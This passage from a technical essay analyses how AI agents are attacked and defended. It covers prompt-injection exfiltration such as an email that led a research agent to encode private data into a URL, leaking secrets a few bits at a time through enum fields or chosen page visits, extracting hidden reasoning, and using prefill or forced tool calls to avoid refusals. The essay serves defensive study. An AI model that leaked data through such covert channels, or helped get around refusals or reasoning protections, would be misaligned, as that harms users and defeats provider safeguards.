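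The model had encoded the name and address before it called the tool, so software looking for personal data in the URL would have found an opaque string. The request also left from OpenAI's servers, so the victim's employer couldn't have caught it by monitoring its own network.

Radware reports that the final version worked every time in repeated tests. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces part of what is evidently the same email and reports that it worked 50% of the time. The difference hardly matters, because the attack takes only one email and can be repeated.

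Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling the researchers, and marked it as resolved on 3 September. It hasn't said exactly what it changed, but it has since described its current safeguard, Safe Url, which covers Deep Research's searches and page visits. According to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), the agent may automatically fetch a URL only if the company's crawler has already found it on the public web. The crawler has no access to conversations, so its index is very unlikely to include a URL newly built to contain a private address. If there is no match, the agent has to try another site or the user gets a warning.

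### How much one argument can carry

The index turns the URL from free text into a choice from a very long list. That choice can still carry a secret, but more slowly. By the measure applied to the support assistant's response schema, a field with 8 permitted values carries at most log₂ 8 = 3 bits per call. A 128-bit secret, the size of a common encryption key, would therefore take at least 43 calls (128 / 3 ≈ 42.7). A free-text field of 100 characters drawn from 64 symbols can carry log₂ 64 = 6 bits per character, or 600 bits in total, so one call is enough.

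| Field | Most it can carry per call | Calls for a 128-bit secret |
|---|---|---|
| True or false | 1 bit | 128 |
| Enum with 8 values | 3 bits | 43 |
| Enum with 500 product names | 9.0 bits | 15 |
| Whole number from 1 to 1,000,000 | 19.9 bits | 7 |
| 100 characters from 64 symbols | 600 bits | 1 |

These are upper limits because they assume that the attacker receives every value in the right order and that the model encodes the secret without mistakes. A model following instructions on a web page may well encode it wrongly. An enum sent to a tool whose inputs the attacker can't observe leaks nothing.

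However, the limits for several fields add up, and the choice of tool counts as a field too. If an attacker can see which of 16 tools the agent called, that choice can leak up to 4 bits. Many secrets are also much smaller than a key. A four-digit PIN has about 13.3 bits, so five calls with the 8-value enum could leak all of it. Limiting an application to ten such calls per session would cap the leak at 30 bits, which protects the key in that session but not the PIN.

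The same arithmetic applies to OpenAI's index. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on a security researcher's blog, points out that an attacker could assign a letter or digit to each of 36 already indexed pages. Each visit would then leak about 5.2 bits, so a 128-bit secret would take 25 visits. OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges this weakness.

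The post suggests stopping the agent from visiting the same URL twice in a session. With 36 pages, the set of pages visited could then reveal at most 36 bits. The order of the visits could raise that to about 140 bits, but requests may arrive out of order, which makes the order less useful to an attacker. A larger site would raise both figures, so the measure limits the leak but doesn't stop it.

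### Tools that can't work without free text

Closed-choice fields are enough for some fairly complex tasks. Goedecke discusses Jev, a model that answers only by picking from choices supplied with the question. Jev can play the video game Doom in real time by choosing its current goal, which key to press and whether to hold down the trigger. An agent that routed support tickets or moved appointments between open slots could work in the same way. But such a model can't write anything long, and several of the most useful tools are made to receive long text.

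Email templates work for confirming a booking, but not for answering a customer's unusual question. The recipient is easier to restrict than the body, but restricting it would not have helped in the picnic example, because the attacker was the person the user wanted to answer.

A search query has to describe what the user wants to know, and no developer can list every possibility in advance. For databases, a company can replace free-form queries with prepared reports that each take a few typed parameters. That suits a support desk, but it would prevent an analyst from asking questions that nobody had foreseen.

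Code is the hardest tool argument to restrict, since a short program can build any string and send it anywhere its environment allows. Restricting the environment makes more sense. For example, OpenAI runs the small applications that ChatGPT creates in a sandbox, which detects unexpected communication and asks the user for consent.

The danger of the free text depends on where it goes. A query to a company's own database normally stays inside the company, while an email leaves it. OpenAI analyses its products in terms of sources, through which an attacker can influence the agent, and sinks, through which the agent can do damage. An agent is safe from this attack if it reads only trusted text or has no access to a sink, but most useful agents read untrusted text and can also send data out.

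Short fields have a related problem, because their values often have to come from material the user didn't write. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) classified the user tasks in the AgentDojo benchmark, where agents work with simulated banks, chat channels and travel sites while reading planted instructions. In 11 of the 16 banking tasks, the user names the action but leaves some detail for the agent to find. A typical task is to pay a bill whose amount and payee are both in a file. An enum written before the agent opened the file couldn't contain the payee. A rule barring untrusted values from arguments would make the task impossible.

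These tasks are also more vulnerable to attack. With GPT-4o-mini and no defence, AgentDojo's standard attack succeeded 43.3% of the time when the user's request specified everything, and 63.9% when the agent had to look up details. It succeeded 87.5% of the time when the user relied on a document to specify the action, as in "do everything on my to-do list", though that figure is based on only 24 cases.

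### CaMeL's separation of plan and data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), is the main attempt to control arguments through the design of the agent. It makes one model write the whole plan, as a program, before anything untrusted has been read. For the picnic, a simplified program might be:

```python
invitation = read_email("picnic invitation")
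date = extract(invitation, "date of the picnic")
if is_free(date):
    send_email(to=invitation.sender, body="Yes, I'll be there.")
```

The planning model works from the user's request and never reads the invitation. The `extract` step calls a second, quarantined model, which reads the invitation but has no tools and can't change the program. The hidden sentence reaches only this second model, where at worst it causes a wrong date.

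An interpreter runs the program and records the origin of every value. Here the date and the recipient came from the invitation, and the body came from the plan. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks those origins against a policy. If the user had asked the agent to suggest some free afternoons, the body would contain values from the calendar, and the policy would have to specify whether the organizer may see them. This is called information-flow control. FIDES, the agent from the previous section that hides sensitive results in variables, is another example. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) describes FIDES's labels as covering both confidentiality (who may learn a value) and integrity (how far to trust it).

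Even this program leaks one bit of the calendar. The organizer learns from the reply that the user is free that day, although no argument contains that information. CaMeL has a strict mode that tracks such implicit flows, but a policy that blocked this one would also block the reply the user asked for.

### What CaMeL costs in completed tasks

Ma and colleagues tested agents with and without CaMeL on 57 AgentDojo tasks, with no attacks. CaMeL reduced task completion from 66.7% to 26.3% with GPT-4o-mini and from 70.2% to 40.4% with Claude Haiku 4.5. They rate CaMeL the most effective overall of their ten defences, but it also reduced task completion the most on four of five models. *AgentSys* (2026) reports similar results from a separate test of CaMeL on GPT-4o-mini, with 30.0% of tasks completed and no successful attacks.

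Part of the drop in task completion may come from how tools are documented. A function definition specifies a tool's inputs but usually doesn't describe its output. An ordinary agent can work without that description because it reads the result before deciding what to do next, but CaMeL's planner has to write code that handles the result before it exists. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to groups of agents, had to add full return schemas to every tool description to get reasonable completion rates, and notes that CaMeL's original evaluation needed them too. The paper describes this as modest work that a developer does once for each set of tools. A test that left the schemas out would make CaMeL look worse than it is.

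The planning model matters as well. Writing a correct program without seeing tool results is harder than choosing one call at a time, and GPT-4o-mini is a small model from 2024. The smaller loss on Claude Haiku 4.5 fits this explanation, although two models are too few to establish a trend.

The other limitation is that some tasks can't be planned in advance, even by a better planner. A checkout page may require the customer to log in, and the login may require a code from an email that doesn't exist yet. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) counted only 6 such tasks among AgentDojo's 97, so the need to replan can't explain most of the losses above. They then built a benchmark of 60 tasks that all require replanning. CaMeL completed none of them with any of four models, while an undefended GPT-4o completed 53.3%. CaMeL's attack success rate was also zero, but this is weak evidence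 of security because the agent completed no tasks.

A fixed plan is less suited to agents that operate a computer through its screen. According to *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), an AgentDojo plan averages 4.9 tool calls. A basic CaMeL plan for computer use needs 19.8, and the paper's improved planning method, which adds steps to observe and verify the screen, needs 41.1.

### False data in a sound plan

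CaMeL protects the agent's plan, but an attacker may only need to change the data the plan uses. If an attacker formats a bill so that the quarantined model extracts the wrong account number, the agent will pay the wrong person while still following the plan. A false email address could misdirect a confidential report in the same way.

*Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) tests these attacks. They succeeded 49.1% of the time against an undefended agent, 25.0% against CaMeL with its policies off, and 23.1% with the policies on. One reason the policies didn't stop more attacks was a fault in the implementation. When the quarantined model extracted a value, CaMeL lost the record of where it came from, so the policy treated untrusted data as safe.

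That fault can be repaired, and the policy could then block payments to any payee taken from an untrusted file. But it would also block payment of the legitimate bill in AgentDojo's banking task. Both the attacker's account number and the legitimate one come from an untrusted file, so the policy needs other evidence to distinguish them, such as a list of known payees or the user's approval.

Newer designs check where argument values come from without settling the whole plan first. Ma and colleagues cover one such design, ROPE, which four of them helped develop. It accepts a sensitive argument only if the value can be traced back to the user. On AgentDojo, ROPE lowered task completion by at most 7 percentage points. On AgentDyn, GPT-4o-mini completed 43.3% of tasks with ROPE and 46.7% without it, and attacks tailored to the defended agent succeeded 2.9% of the time instead of 59.1%. Gemini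 2.5 Flash's task completion fell more, from 36.7% to 25.0%.

PACE also decides call by call. It compares the effects of each call with what the user's request authorizes, and traces whether protected data or untrusted text could have influenced the arguments. It also searches the arguments for known secrets in a fixed set of encodings. This search would help with a URL like ShadowLeak's, but it misses secrets that the model paraphrases, translates or splits up.

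On eight benchmarks, PACE reduced task completion by at most three points, and it had or tied for the lowest attack success rate in 76 of 79 comparisons. The version tested can let a blocked call through if the call's effects appear authorized. The formal guarantees apply to a stricter version that Li, Wang and colleagues didn't evaluate, and which presumably blocks more legitimate calls.

### Allowlists, confirmation and training

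A destination allowlist is simpler than tracking origins. The agent may send data only to approved sites or addresses, whatever the argument contains. OpenAI considered a list of trusted sites for ChatGPT but judged it inadequate, partly because many reputable sites have links that redirect elsewhere, and partly because people visit far more sites than the list would cover. Checking the exact URL can block an address built from private data even when the site is trusted. But it also stops the agent from opening pages that no crawler could have found, such as a personal order-tracking link or a results page whose address includes the user's search terms. OpenAI hasn't published how often this happens.

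An allowlist of email recipients works well for a company agent that writes only to colleagues, but it fails for a sales agent that has to answer people who have never written to the company before.

Asking the user to confirm handles some of these cases. When Safe Url detects that a request would send information from the conversation to a third party, ChatGPT either blocks the request or shows the user the information and asks whether to send it. A user who sees "Dentist, Tuesday 3 p.m." in a reply about a picnic will probably notice that it doesn't belong. But users can't interpret an encoded string, as in ShadowLeak, so the warning has to explain the risk without relying on them to read the data.

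Confirmation is also least useful where agents save the most time. A task in AgentDyn takes 7.1 steps on average, so approving each one would mean about seven prompts per task, and OpenAI cautions that frequent warnings train people to click through them. During a scheduled job or a half-hour research run, nobody may be there to answer. In tests by Li, Wen and colleagues, agents often stopped to ask for approval and left the task unfinished, so the researchers told them to proceed without asking. Their results therefore don't measure how much protection confirmation would have given.

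They did measure several other defences. The table gives results with GPT-4o, except for Meta SecAlign, a version of Llama 3.3 70B that its developers trained to resist injected instructions. Tool Filter sets an allowlist of tools, rather than destinations, when the task starts. Progent updates the permitted tools as the task proceeds, and DRIFT begins with a plan but can approve departures from it.

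| Defence | Tasks completed without attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 37.8% |
| Tool Filter | 8.3% | 4.2% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 1.7% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 0.8% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 0% |
| Meta SecAlign | 55.0% | 9.0% |

Tool Filter usually removed tools that seemed irrelevant to the request but turned out to be essential later, such as the email tool needed to fetch a login code. Progent gradually blocked almost everything on long tasks. Training keeps far more tasks working because it leaves every tool and argument available, but the model may lose the ability to follow outside instructions that are part of the job, such as a website's request to log in. Every AgentDyn task includes an instruction of this kind, and Meta SecAlign still completed over half of the tasks.

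The security benefit of the training is harder to measure. The ordinary Llama 3.3 70B had an attack success rate of 11.9%, compared with 9.0% after training, but it completed only 10.0% of the tasks. An agent that rarely gets far with the user's task may also rarely get far with an attacker's, so the small difference probably understates the benefit. Still, 9.0% is high for an agent that reads many strangers' emails, especially since the attack was a fixed, well-known template. On AgentDojo's easier tasks, the trained model's rate was 1.9%.

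Newer commercial models do better. AgentDojo's standard attack succeeded against Claude Haiku 4.5, with no added defence, in 0.3% of cases. Li, Wen and colleagues suspect that developers have trained recent models on that attack's template, so the figure may understate the model's vulnerability. Ma and colleagues therefore had another model rewrite the injected text up to six times, with only the success or failure of each version as feedback. The rewritten attacks succeeded in 2.9% of the cases where the agent had to look up an argument's value, and in none of the others. OpenAI says that safety training also defeats most of the attacks on ChatGPT that the company knows of, and that Safe Url is meant for the ones that get through.

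## Hidden reasoning leaking into visible fields

Output fields and tool arguments can also expose the reasoning a model writes before it answers, which the provider wants to keep secret. Function calling makes the reasoning harder to hide, because the model needs it again every time a tool returns a result.

### Why providers hide reasoning

One reason is distillation, training one model on the outputs of another. According to Anthropic's help centre article *Preserved thinking*, distillers use thousands of fake accounts, and the models they train can gain capabilities without the safeguards against misuse.

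Reasoning is more useful to a distiller than answers. In *Hidden Thoughts Are Not Secret*, Lu, Tsai and colleagues (2026) trained a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, on different outputs of a larger one, Qwen3-14B. The table shows the small model's average score across five mathematics and programming benchmarks.

| Training material | Average score |
|---|---|
| None | 26.0% |
| Answers only | 15.2% |
| Summaries of the reasoning | 26.0% |
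| Full internal reasoning | 32.2% |

Training on answers alone made the small model worse, presumably because it learned to answer without working anything out. Training on summaries did not change the average, which supports the common practice of showing users a summary at most. The results were similar with the larger Qwen3-32B as the teacher. Lu and colleagues chose each trained model's best version using these same benchmarks, so the last three scores are probably a little high.

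Reasoning can also contain material that doesn't belong in the answer. In *Stealing Reasoning Traces from Proprietary LLM APIs* (August 2026), Panfilov, Schmotz and colleagues reported that they could recover hidden reasoning from Anthropic, OpenAI and Google models, including private data and hazardous details that the models had left out of their answers. They recovered 367 items of personal information and 182 credentials from 315,320 encrypted blocks of reasoning in public repositories. The people who posted the blocks couldn't read them, so they couldn't have redacted this information.

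### Carrying reasoning from one tool call to the next

When a tool returns its result, the model needs the reasoning that led to the call in order to continue. But the application resends the conversation with each result, and on Anthropic's standard API that conversation includes reasoning Anthropic doesn't want the application to read.

Anthropic uses encryption to keep reasoning hidden while carrying it across tool calls. According to Anthropic's *Thinking*, the API returns reasoning in thinking blocks, each with an encrypted copy of the full text. The application sends the blocks back unchanged with the tool result, and the server decrypts them and puts the reasoning back into the prompt. The readable part of a block contains at most a summary written by a different model, and on newer models it is empty by default.

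Discarding the reasoning after each call would be safer, but it can make an agent perform worse. A bug in one of Anthropic's products kept deleting earlier reasoning, sometimes in the middle of a tool-use loop. Anthropic says Claude carried on "increasingly without memory of why it had chosen to do what it was doing". Users noticed forgetfulness, repetition and odd choices of tools.

The provider could instead store the reasoning on its own servers. OpenAI's Responses API can do this for the o1 and o3 models, according to *'Thinking' / 'Reasoning Content'*, a documentation page for LiteLLM, a library that connects applications to many providers. The application then sends only the previous response's identifier, so its logs contain no encrypted reasoning to leak. However, server-side storage is hard to reconcile with zero-retention agreements. Anthropic began testing server-side conversations,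 called message threads, on 2 November 2026. It deletes each thread within an hour of its last use, according to its *Claude Platform release notes* (2026).

Under either arrangement, once the server has put the reasoning back into the prompt, the model can copy it into any field that accepts free text.

### Reasoning in explanation fields and tool arguments

Developers often ask for an explanation as part of a structured output. A program that sorts support tickets might want this:

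```json
{
  "reasoning": "The customer was charged twice for one order.",
  "category": "billing"
}
```

The order of the fields matters because the model writes "reasoning" first and then conditions the category on it. If the model has no hidden reasoning, the field lets it work through the problem before choosing a category. A model that has already reasoned in private needs the field less, but the developer may still want a record for staff who review the decisions. As with the body of an email, the schema can't distinguish this one sentence from pages of copied reasoning.

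In *What Is Reasoning* (2026), Ronacher explains that hidden reasoning is ordinary text that the model has learned to put in a separate part of its response. In gpt-oss, OpenAI's open-weight model, a special token marks where the reasoning starts, and a parser sends what follows to a separate stream. So if the model doesn't produce that token, its reasoning goes wherever the rest of its output goes.

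Ronacher has seen older models do this in tool calls when thinking was turned off, writing their thoughts into shell commands that discarded the text. He also found that a custom tool for recording thoughts could draw out some reasoning, but only with the model's native reasoning turned off. In these cases the model used the tool argument in place of hidden reasoning, so it wasn't copying from a private block. But the developer could still read the kind of text the provider had a reason to keep private.

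Anthropic reports a similar problem with Claude Opus 5, which can occasionally include internal tags in its visible output when thinking is off. Developers can't turn thinking off on Opus 5.5 or the Fable models. That should make this kind of displacement less common, although Anthropic doesn't give this as the reason for the restriction.

### Measurements of ordinary text

Lu and colleagues tested whether a prompt could make a model repeat its hidden reasoning in its visible answer. Their prompts contained worked examples whose answers included the reasoning. They used open-weight models so that they could compare the hidden reasoning with the visible answer.

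The paper measures only ordinary text and doesn't test schema fields or constrained decoding. One set of examples imitated an agent's tool call, but no tool ran and the model wrote no real arguments.

ROUGE-L scores the overlap between two texts from 0 to 1, based on the longest sequence of words they share in the same order. When the prompt simply asked Qwen3-14B to repeat its internal reasoning, the visible text scored 0.13 against that reasoning across 500 questions. Examples in a plain format raised the score only to 0.16. Examples that looked like code or tool output raised it to 0.45–0.48, with the imitation tool call at about 0.46.

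Lu and colleagues suggest that models learn to withhold reasoning mainly in conversation, and that code-like formats fall outside what they learned. The 2024 function-calling study offered a similar explanation for weaker refusals in function calls. If this explanation is right, real tool arguments could also be vulnerable, but the imitation format provides only indirect evidence of that.

With the best format and full-length texts, overlap was 0.62 to 0.64 on four models, 0.26 on gpt-oss-20b and 0.19 on the largest Qwen3 model. Lu and colleagues call one of the four, Qwen3.6-27B, "essentially immune" because its visible text had little in common with the reasoning it produced for an ordinary prompt, but the visible text's overlap with its reasoning under the attack was 0.62. The attack seems to have changed how the model reasoned, and the model then repeated much of that reasoning.

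The visible reasoning was also useful for distillation. Small models trained on it averaged 29.9% on the five benchmarks, or 31.5% when the training examples included only correct answers. That is close to the 32.2% average for models trained on the internal reasoning.

Lu and colleagues didn't run the attack on commercial models, because the providers' terms restrict this kind of extraction. Those services may have filters that the tested models lacked, so the results don't show how much hidden reasoning Claude or GPT would put in a "reasoning" field.

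### Tying reasoning to a conversation and an account

Anthropic says that altering earlier turns of a conversation is a common way to extract reasoning. Since releasing Claude Fable 5.1 on 1 September 2026, it has therefore checked that each thinking block comes back with the same system prompt, tools and messages that preceded it. Anthropic calls this preserved thinking.

Panfilov and colleagues describe one way to build such a check. The provider computes a hash, a short fingerprint of the conversation so far, and includes it in the encrypted block. When the block comes back, the server computes the hash again and compares the two. If even one character of the conversation has changed, the hashes differ and the block fails verification.

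Some models' thinking blocks also work only in the account that produced them, or in a linked account such as another in the same parent organization. This makes a leaked transcript less dangerous. It also makes it harder for distillers to move their material to new accounts after Anthropic bans the old ones. The rules differ by model:

| Models | History check on accounts created from 31 August 2026 | History check on older accounts | Blocks tied to an account |
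|---|---|---|---|
| Fable 5.2, Mythos 5.2 | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Sonnet 5.5, Haiku 5.5 | Yes | No | Yes |
| Fable 5.1, Opus 5.5 | Yes | No | No |

Anthropic started with new accounts because it sees the most distillation there. Both checks protect the encrypted blocks, but they can't stop a model from writing its reasoning into a visible field during an unaltered conversation.

### What the history check costs developers

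Many agents change their own history for good reasons. For example, a travel agent may start with a tool for searching flights, and the application adds a booking tool once the customer has chosen a flight. Editing the tool list changes what came before every thinking block in the conversation, so the next request fails. If the application edits a message just before the fourth of ten thinking blocks, blocks four to ten become invalid.

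The API returns an error by default, and retrying the same request won't help. The developer can instead set the API to drop the invalid blocks. The request then succeeds, but the model loses the reasoning in those blocks and may use significantly more tokens to redo it, so Anthropic recommends this only as a stopgap.

Anthropic offers substitutes for the most common edits, all of them in beta:

| What the developer wants to do | Substitute |
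|---|---|
| Shorten a long history | The API writes a signed summary to replace older messages, and recent turns can keep their reasoning |
| Add or remove tools | A system message later in the conversation makes the change, leaving the original list alone |
| Give a reminder for one turn | A temporary system message applies to that turn, then stays in the history at no token cost |

These substitutes cover the travel agent's case well, because the application can append the booking tool instead of rewriting the list. But each one requires new code, and not every cloud platform offers all of them. Agents that already avoid editing their history need few changes. They also save money, because the server can reuse its cached copy of the conversation. On Fable 5.1, 200,000 tokens cost $2.00 to process afresh and 5 cents to read from the cache.

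If a customer pastes a password into a chat, deleting it from the history may not be enough, because the model may have repeated it in reasoning the application can't read. Anthropic's developer guide *Preserved thinking* therefore advises removing every thinking block after the secret first appears. It gives the same advice for text that an attacker has injected. The agent then loses all its reasoning from that point on, including the parts unrelated to the secret.

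Switching models can also lose reasoning. If Fable 5.2 refuses a request and another model takes over, the replacement can't read Fable 5.2's thinking blocks. The API leaves them out without returning an error. Fable 5.2 can use them again when the conversation returns to it, if the application has kept them.

People who build tools for other developers may not notice the problem in testing. Anthropic warns that these toolmakers' own accounts are probably old enough to be exempt from the check on some models, while their users' accounts may not be. OpenRouter, a service that passes requests on to many providers, says that enforcement for Fable 5.1 depends on which provider handles the request. It advises developers to add to a conversation's history but not change what is already there.

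### Refusals for reasoning extraction

Anthropic says that on several recent models, a tool can trigger a `reasoning_extraction` refusal if its input has a field for reasoning or its description asks for reasoning. Schemas that ask for step-by-step reasoning can trigger the same refusal.

This affects honest developers. The ticket-sorting schema above has a "reasoning" field, although its developer wants only a sentence for the record. Anthropic still allows requests for a short explanation, a summary or the evidence behind a result. The developer could rename the field "evidence" and describe it as "one sentence that identifies the relevant fact in the ticket". Renaming the field might not be enough if its description still asked for every step.

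An attacker can rename a field, so a filter that checked only for suspicious names would be easy to evade. An effective filter would have to analyze the content of the request or the model's output. It would then be difficult to distinguish leaked reasoning from a legitimate answer, because a detailed explanation of a mathematical proof may look much like the reasoning that produced it.

Since 24 September, Anthropic has charged for these refusals even when they arrive before any output. It says it measures few false positives in this category but gives no rate. A developer whose agent sends a long history with each request could pay for that history repeatedly before noticing which field causes the refusals. Anthropic also tells developers to change the prompt instead of retrying on another model, the automatic fallback they use for other refusals.

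### Progress notes between tool calls

Between tool calls, agents often tell the user what they are doing. A coding agent might report that it has found the cause of a bug and is about to edit a file. On recent models, including Fable 5.2, Opus 5.5 and Sonnet 5.5, Anthropic returns these notes as thinking blocks rather than ordinary text. The readable part of these blocks is empty by default, so an application that displays the notes may have nothing to show.

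Anthropic's substitute is a display setting called "updates", also in beta, which returns a summary of each note but keeps the other reasoning hidden. A setting called "summarized" returns summaries of both, but the application can't distinguish them. Since the notes describe what the model has found and what it plans to do next, moving them probably also removes a place where reasoning could become visible, though Anthropic doesn't say that this was the purpose.

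The setting only partly restores the old behaviour. A note can take several seconds to appear, and the model may skip it. OpenRouter found that requests outside multi-tool loops returned no text under "updates", and that Fable 5.1 writes fewer notes than Fable 5. An application can work around this by displaying its own status line based on the tool's name, such as "Editing a file", but the line won't include the model's reason for using the tool.

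OpenAI handles these notes differently, advising that the model send a short, visible update before the first tool call of a long task (quoted in Willison, 2026, *GPT-5.5 prompting guide*). The update acknowledges the request and states the first step, so it needn't reveal much reasoning.

### How OpenAI and Google responded

All three companies acknowledged the report by Panfilov and colleagues, and the attacks it describes no longer work on their APIs. The companies had been slower to react to another researcher's earlier disclosure, in May 2026, and according to Panfilov and colleagues, they did not at first acknowledge any security implications.

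Panfilov and colleagues say that tighter validation of the encrypted blocks has largely fixed the problem, but they don't break down the changes by company, so it is hard to compare the burden on developers. If OpenAI or Google also ties reasoning to an exact history, agents that edit their conversations could run into the same trouble as on Claude. OpenAI customers who let the server store the reasoning don't have to manage encrypted blocks, but they depend on OpenAI to retain the data.

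OpenAI also appears to filter requests related to hidden reasoning. When Ronacher asked GPT-5.6 Terra to check the spelling and grammar of his post on the subject, its safety filters blocked the request, so he used another company's model. The request was plainly harmless, though one incident doesn't show how often this happens.

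## Anthropic's removal of prefill and forced tool calls

In 2026, Anthropic also removed prefill and forced tool choice from most of its new models. Either feature could prevent a model from refusing, but many developers used them only to get clean JSON.

### Which models reject which control

Anthropic's *What's new in Claude 4.6* lists the removal of prefill among the breaking changes in Opus 4.6. The API returns an error if a request ends with an unfinished answer for the model to continue. Anthropic had taken structured outputs, the main substitute, out of beta a week earlier.

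Forced tool choice lasted longer than prefill. In July, Anthropic still listed only one model that rejected it outright, Claude Mythos Preview, which was available by invitation for defensive security work. Most of the models released since September also reject it.

| Model | Announced in 2026 | Prefill | Forced tool choice |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6 | 5 February | Rejected | Accepted |
| Mythos Preview | 7 April | Rejected | Rejected |
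| Fable 5 | 9 June | Rejected | Accepted |
| Sonnet 5 | 30 June | Rejected | Accepted |
| Opus 5 | 24 July | Rejected | Accepted |
| Fable 5.1, Mythos 5.1 | 1 September | Rejected | Rejected |
| Opus 5.5 | 22 September | Rejected | Rejected |
| Sonnet 5.5 | 28 September | Rejected | Rejected |
| Haiku 5.5 | 7 October | Rejected | Accepted |
| Fable 5.2, Mythos 5.2 | 9 November | Rejected | Rejected |

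Haiku 5.5 is the exception among the recent models. According to Anthropic's *Claude Haiku 5.5 migration guide*, it accepts a forced tool call but rejects a prefill, even with thinking turned off. Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2 migration guide* describes the restrictions on prefills and forced tool calls as unchanged from the previous versions.

### Whether always-on thinking explains the change

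Anthropic's older page *Choosing a model* and its current documentation both explain that a forced call is itself a prefill, written by the API instead of the developer. The API kept writing these prefills for new models for months after it stopped accepting prefills from developers, and it still writes them on Haiku 5.5, where developers can't.

A model can't think before a forced tool call. The API rejects forced calls combined with manual thinking budgets. With adaptive thinking, where the model decides how much to think, a forced call makes it skip thinking. LiteLLM's *Claude Fable 5.1* links this to the removal of forced tool calls, since thinking is always on in Fable 5.1.

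That can't be the whole explanation. Thinking is also always on in Fable 5, which accepts forced calls. Sonnet 5.5 rejects them even when the developer has turned off the thinking that precedes an answer. Anthropic may have wanted the same rule for most of its new models, or may prefer that they always decide whether to call a tool, but these are guesses. Anthropic's *What's new in Claude Opus 5.5* lists always-on thinking and the end of forced calls as separate breaking changes and gives no reason for the second.

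None of these documents includes a security reason either, although Anthropic does give such reasons for other changes. In October, Anthropic limited the page-fetching tool in its hosted agent service to URLs that had already appeared in the session, saying this reduces the risk of data exfiltration. The lack of a similar explanation for forced calls is weak evidence that security wasn't the main purpose, but a company might also prefer not to advertise a weakness in older models that it still sells.

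Without a forced call, the model can think first and then decline in ordinary prose. In the 2024 study by Wu and colleagues, giving the model the option to decline stopped most of the attacks. However, the 2026 attack by Liu and colleagues doesn't depend on forcing a call. Removing forced tool choice therefore probably stops the simplest attacks of this kind but not the more elaborate ones.

Anthropic also knew that developers used prefill to avoid refusals. Its *Claude Sonnet 5.5 migration guide* lists preventing "unwanted refusals" as one purpose of prefill and says that clear instructions in the user's message are usually enough instead. A developer whose harmless request kept being refused could once have started the answer with "Here is the summary". The same words would have helped a malicious developer get past a justified refusal, and no one could have told from the prefill alone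 which kind of developer had written it.

### One library's invented tool

*The model that wouldn't be forced* (Cockayne, 2026) describes how the change affected go/chat, a Go programming library. The library's `Ask` function takes a question and a data type, derives a JSON Schema from the type, and returns the model's answer in that form.

The library's Claude adapter did this by offering the model a single tool, `submit_response`, with the schema as its input, and forcing the model to call it. The tool never ran, because the adapter needed only the arguments. But the API requires a result after every tool call, so the adapter added a fake one, the word "recorded", to the conversation.

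The 2024 jailbreak was built the same way. A provider looking only at the structure of the request couldn't have told the two apart, so withdrawing the setting disabled both.

Opus 5.5 and Fable 5.1 broke the adapter. Cockayne's first idea was to let the model decide whether to call the tool, and the model called it in both of his trials. He dropped the idea because it meant keeping the invented tool and the fake result, and adding a retry loop for when the model didn't call the tool. He wanted the reply to be valid "because the API constrained it, not because the model chose to comply".

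He therefore sent the schema through structured outputs and offered no tool. The new code is shorter, and the conversation history now contains an ordinary question and answer. Every Claude model he tested accepted the new method, so the adapter doesn't need a separate path for older models.

The library may even have gained a stronger guarantee, because the new version uses constrained decoding and the old code Cockayne prints doesn't turn on strict tool use. The change still took him some time. He drafted the specification in late September and had to wait a week for money before he could test it.

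The migration was this simple because the tool was fake. A developer who needs the model to call a real tool can't just switch to structured outputs.

### Replacements for a forced call

Anthropic offers three replacements, depending on why the developer forced the call.

| Reason for forcing the call | Replacement | What the developer loses |
|---|---|---|
| To make the model use a real tool | Let the model choose, name the tool in the prompt and mark it strict | The guarantee that a call will happen |
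| To get JSON in a fixed shape | Structured outputs without a tool | The tool call itself, which the program may expect |
| To require a call on one turn of a conversation | A system message after the user's latest message | The guarantee that a call will happen, or that it will come first |

In July, Anthropic still recommended combining forced tool choice with strict tool use, which guaranteed that the model would call a tool and that the arguments would match the tool's schema. With the newest models, only the schema match is guaranteed. The Sonnet 5.5 guide says the model can answer without calling the tool.

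How much this matters depends on how often the model skips a call it should make, and the guides give no rate. Cockayne's two successes in two trials are very weak evidence of that rate. To be 95% confident that the model skips fewer than 1% of calls, a developer would need about 300 trials without a failure (0.99²⁹⁹ is just under 5%). Even at a 1% rate, an agent that has to make 100 such calls will miss at least one about 63% of the time (1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰) if the failures are independent.

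Anthropic illustrates the third replacement with a support assistant for an electronics store. A customer asks whether they can still return headphones they have opened. To get the assistant to search the help center before answering, the application adds a system message that requires the model to start this turn with that search.

Changing the old tool choice setting between requests made the server reprocess the messages instead of reading them from its cache. Adding a message leaves everything before it unchanged, so the server can still use its cache, which saves computation in long conversations. But the message is still an instruction, and the model may not follow it.

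Applications that can't tolerate a missing call need to enforce it in their own code. The store could withhold any answer that wasn't preceded by a search, or it could run the search itself with the customer's question as the query and give the model the results. The second approach guarantees the search, but the customer's question may be a worse query than one the model would have written after reading the whole conversation.

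Retrying whenever a reply lacks a tool call is risky because it treats a refusal as an error, which is roughly what Liu and colleagues' attack does when it reports a refusal as a failed check. A safer loop would check for a refusal before retrying and stop after one or two attempts.

### Replacements for a prefill

Developers had used prefill for more varied purposes, so its replacements vary more too. The Sonnet 5.5 guide recommends using structured outputs for formatting, asking in the system prompt for an answer without a preamble, and putting reminders about context in the user's message.

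Without prefill, some uses get more expensive. Anthropic's *API usage primer for Claude* shows how to get the answer to a multiple-choice question by prefilling the response and limiting the output to one token. An enum can restrict the answer to the same letters, but the model also has to write the field's name and the punctuation around it. At Opus 5.5's price of $20 per million output tokens, a million one-token answers would cost $20 and a million ten-token answers $200. On models where thinking is always on, thinking adds to the cost. It also counts toward the output limit, so a request with a very low limit can end before the model starts its answer.

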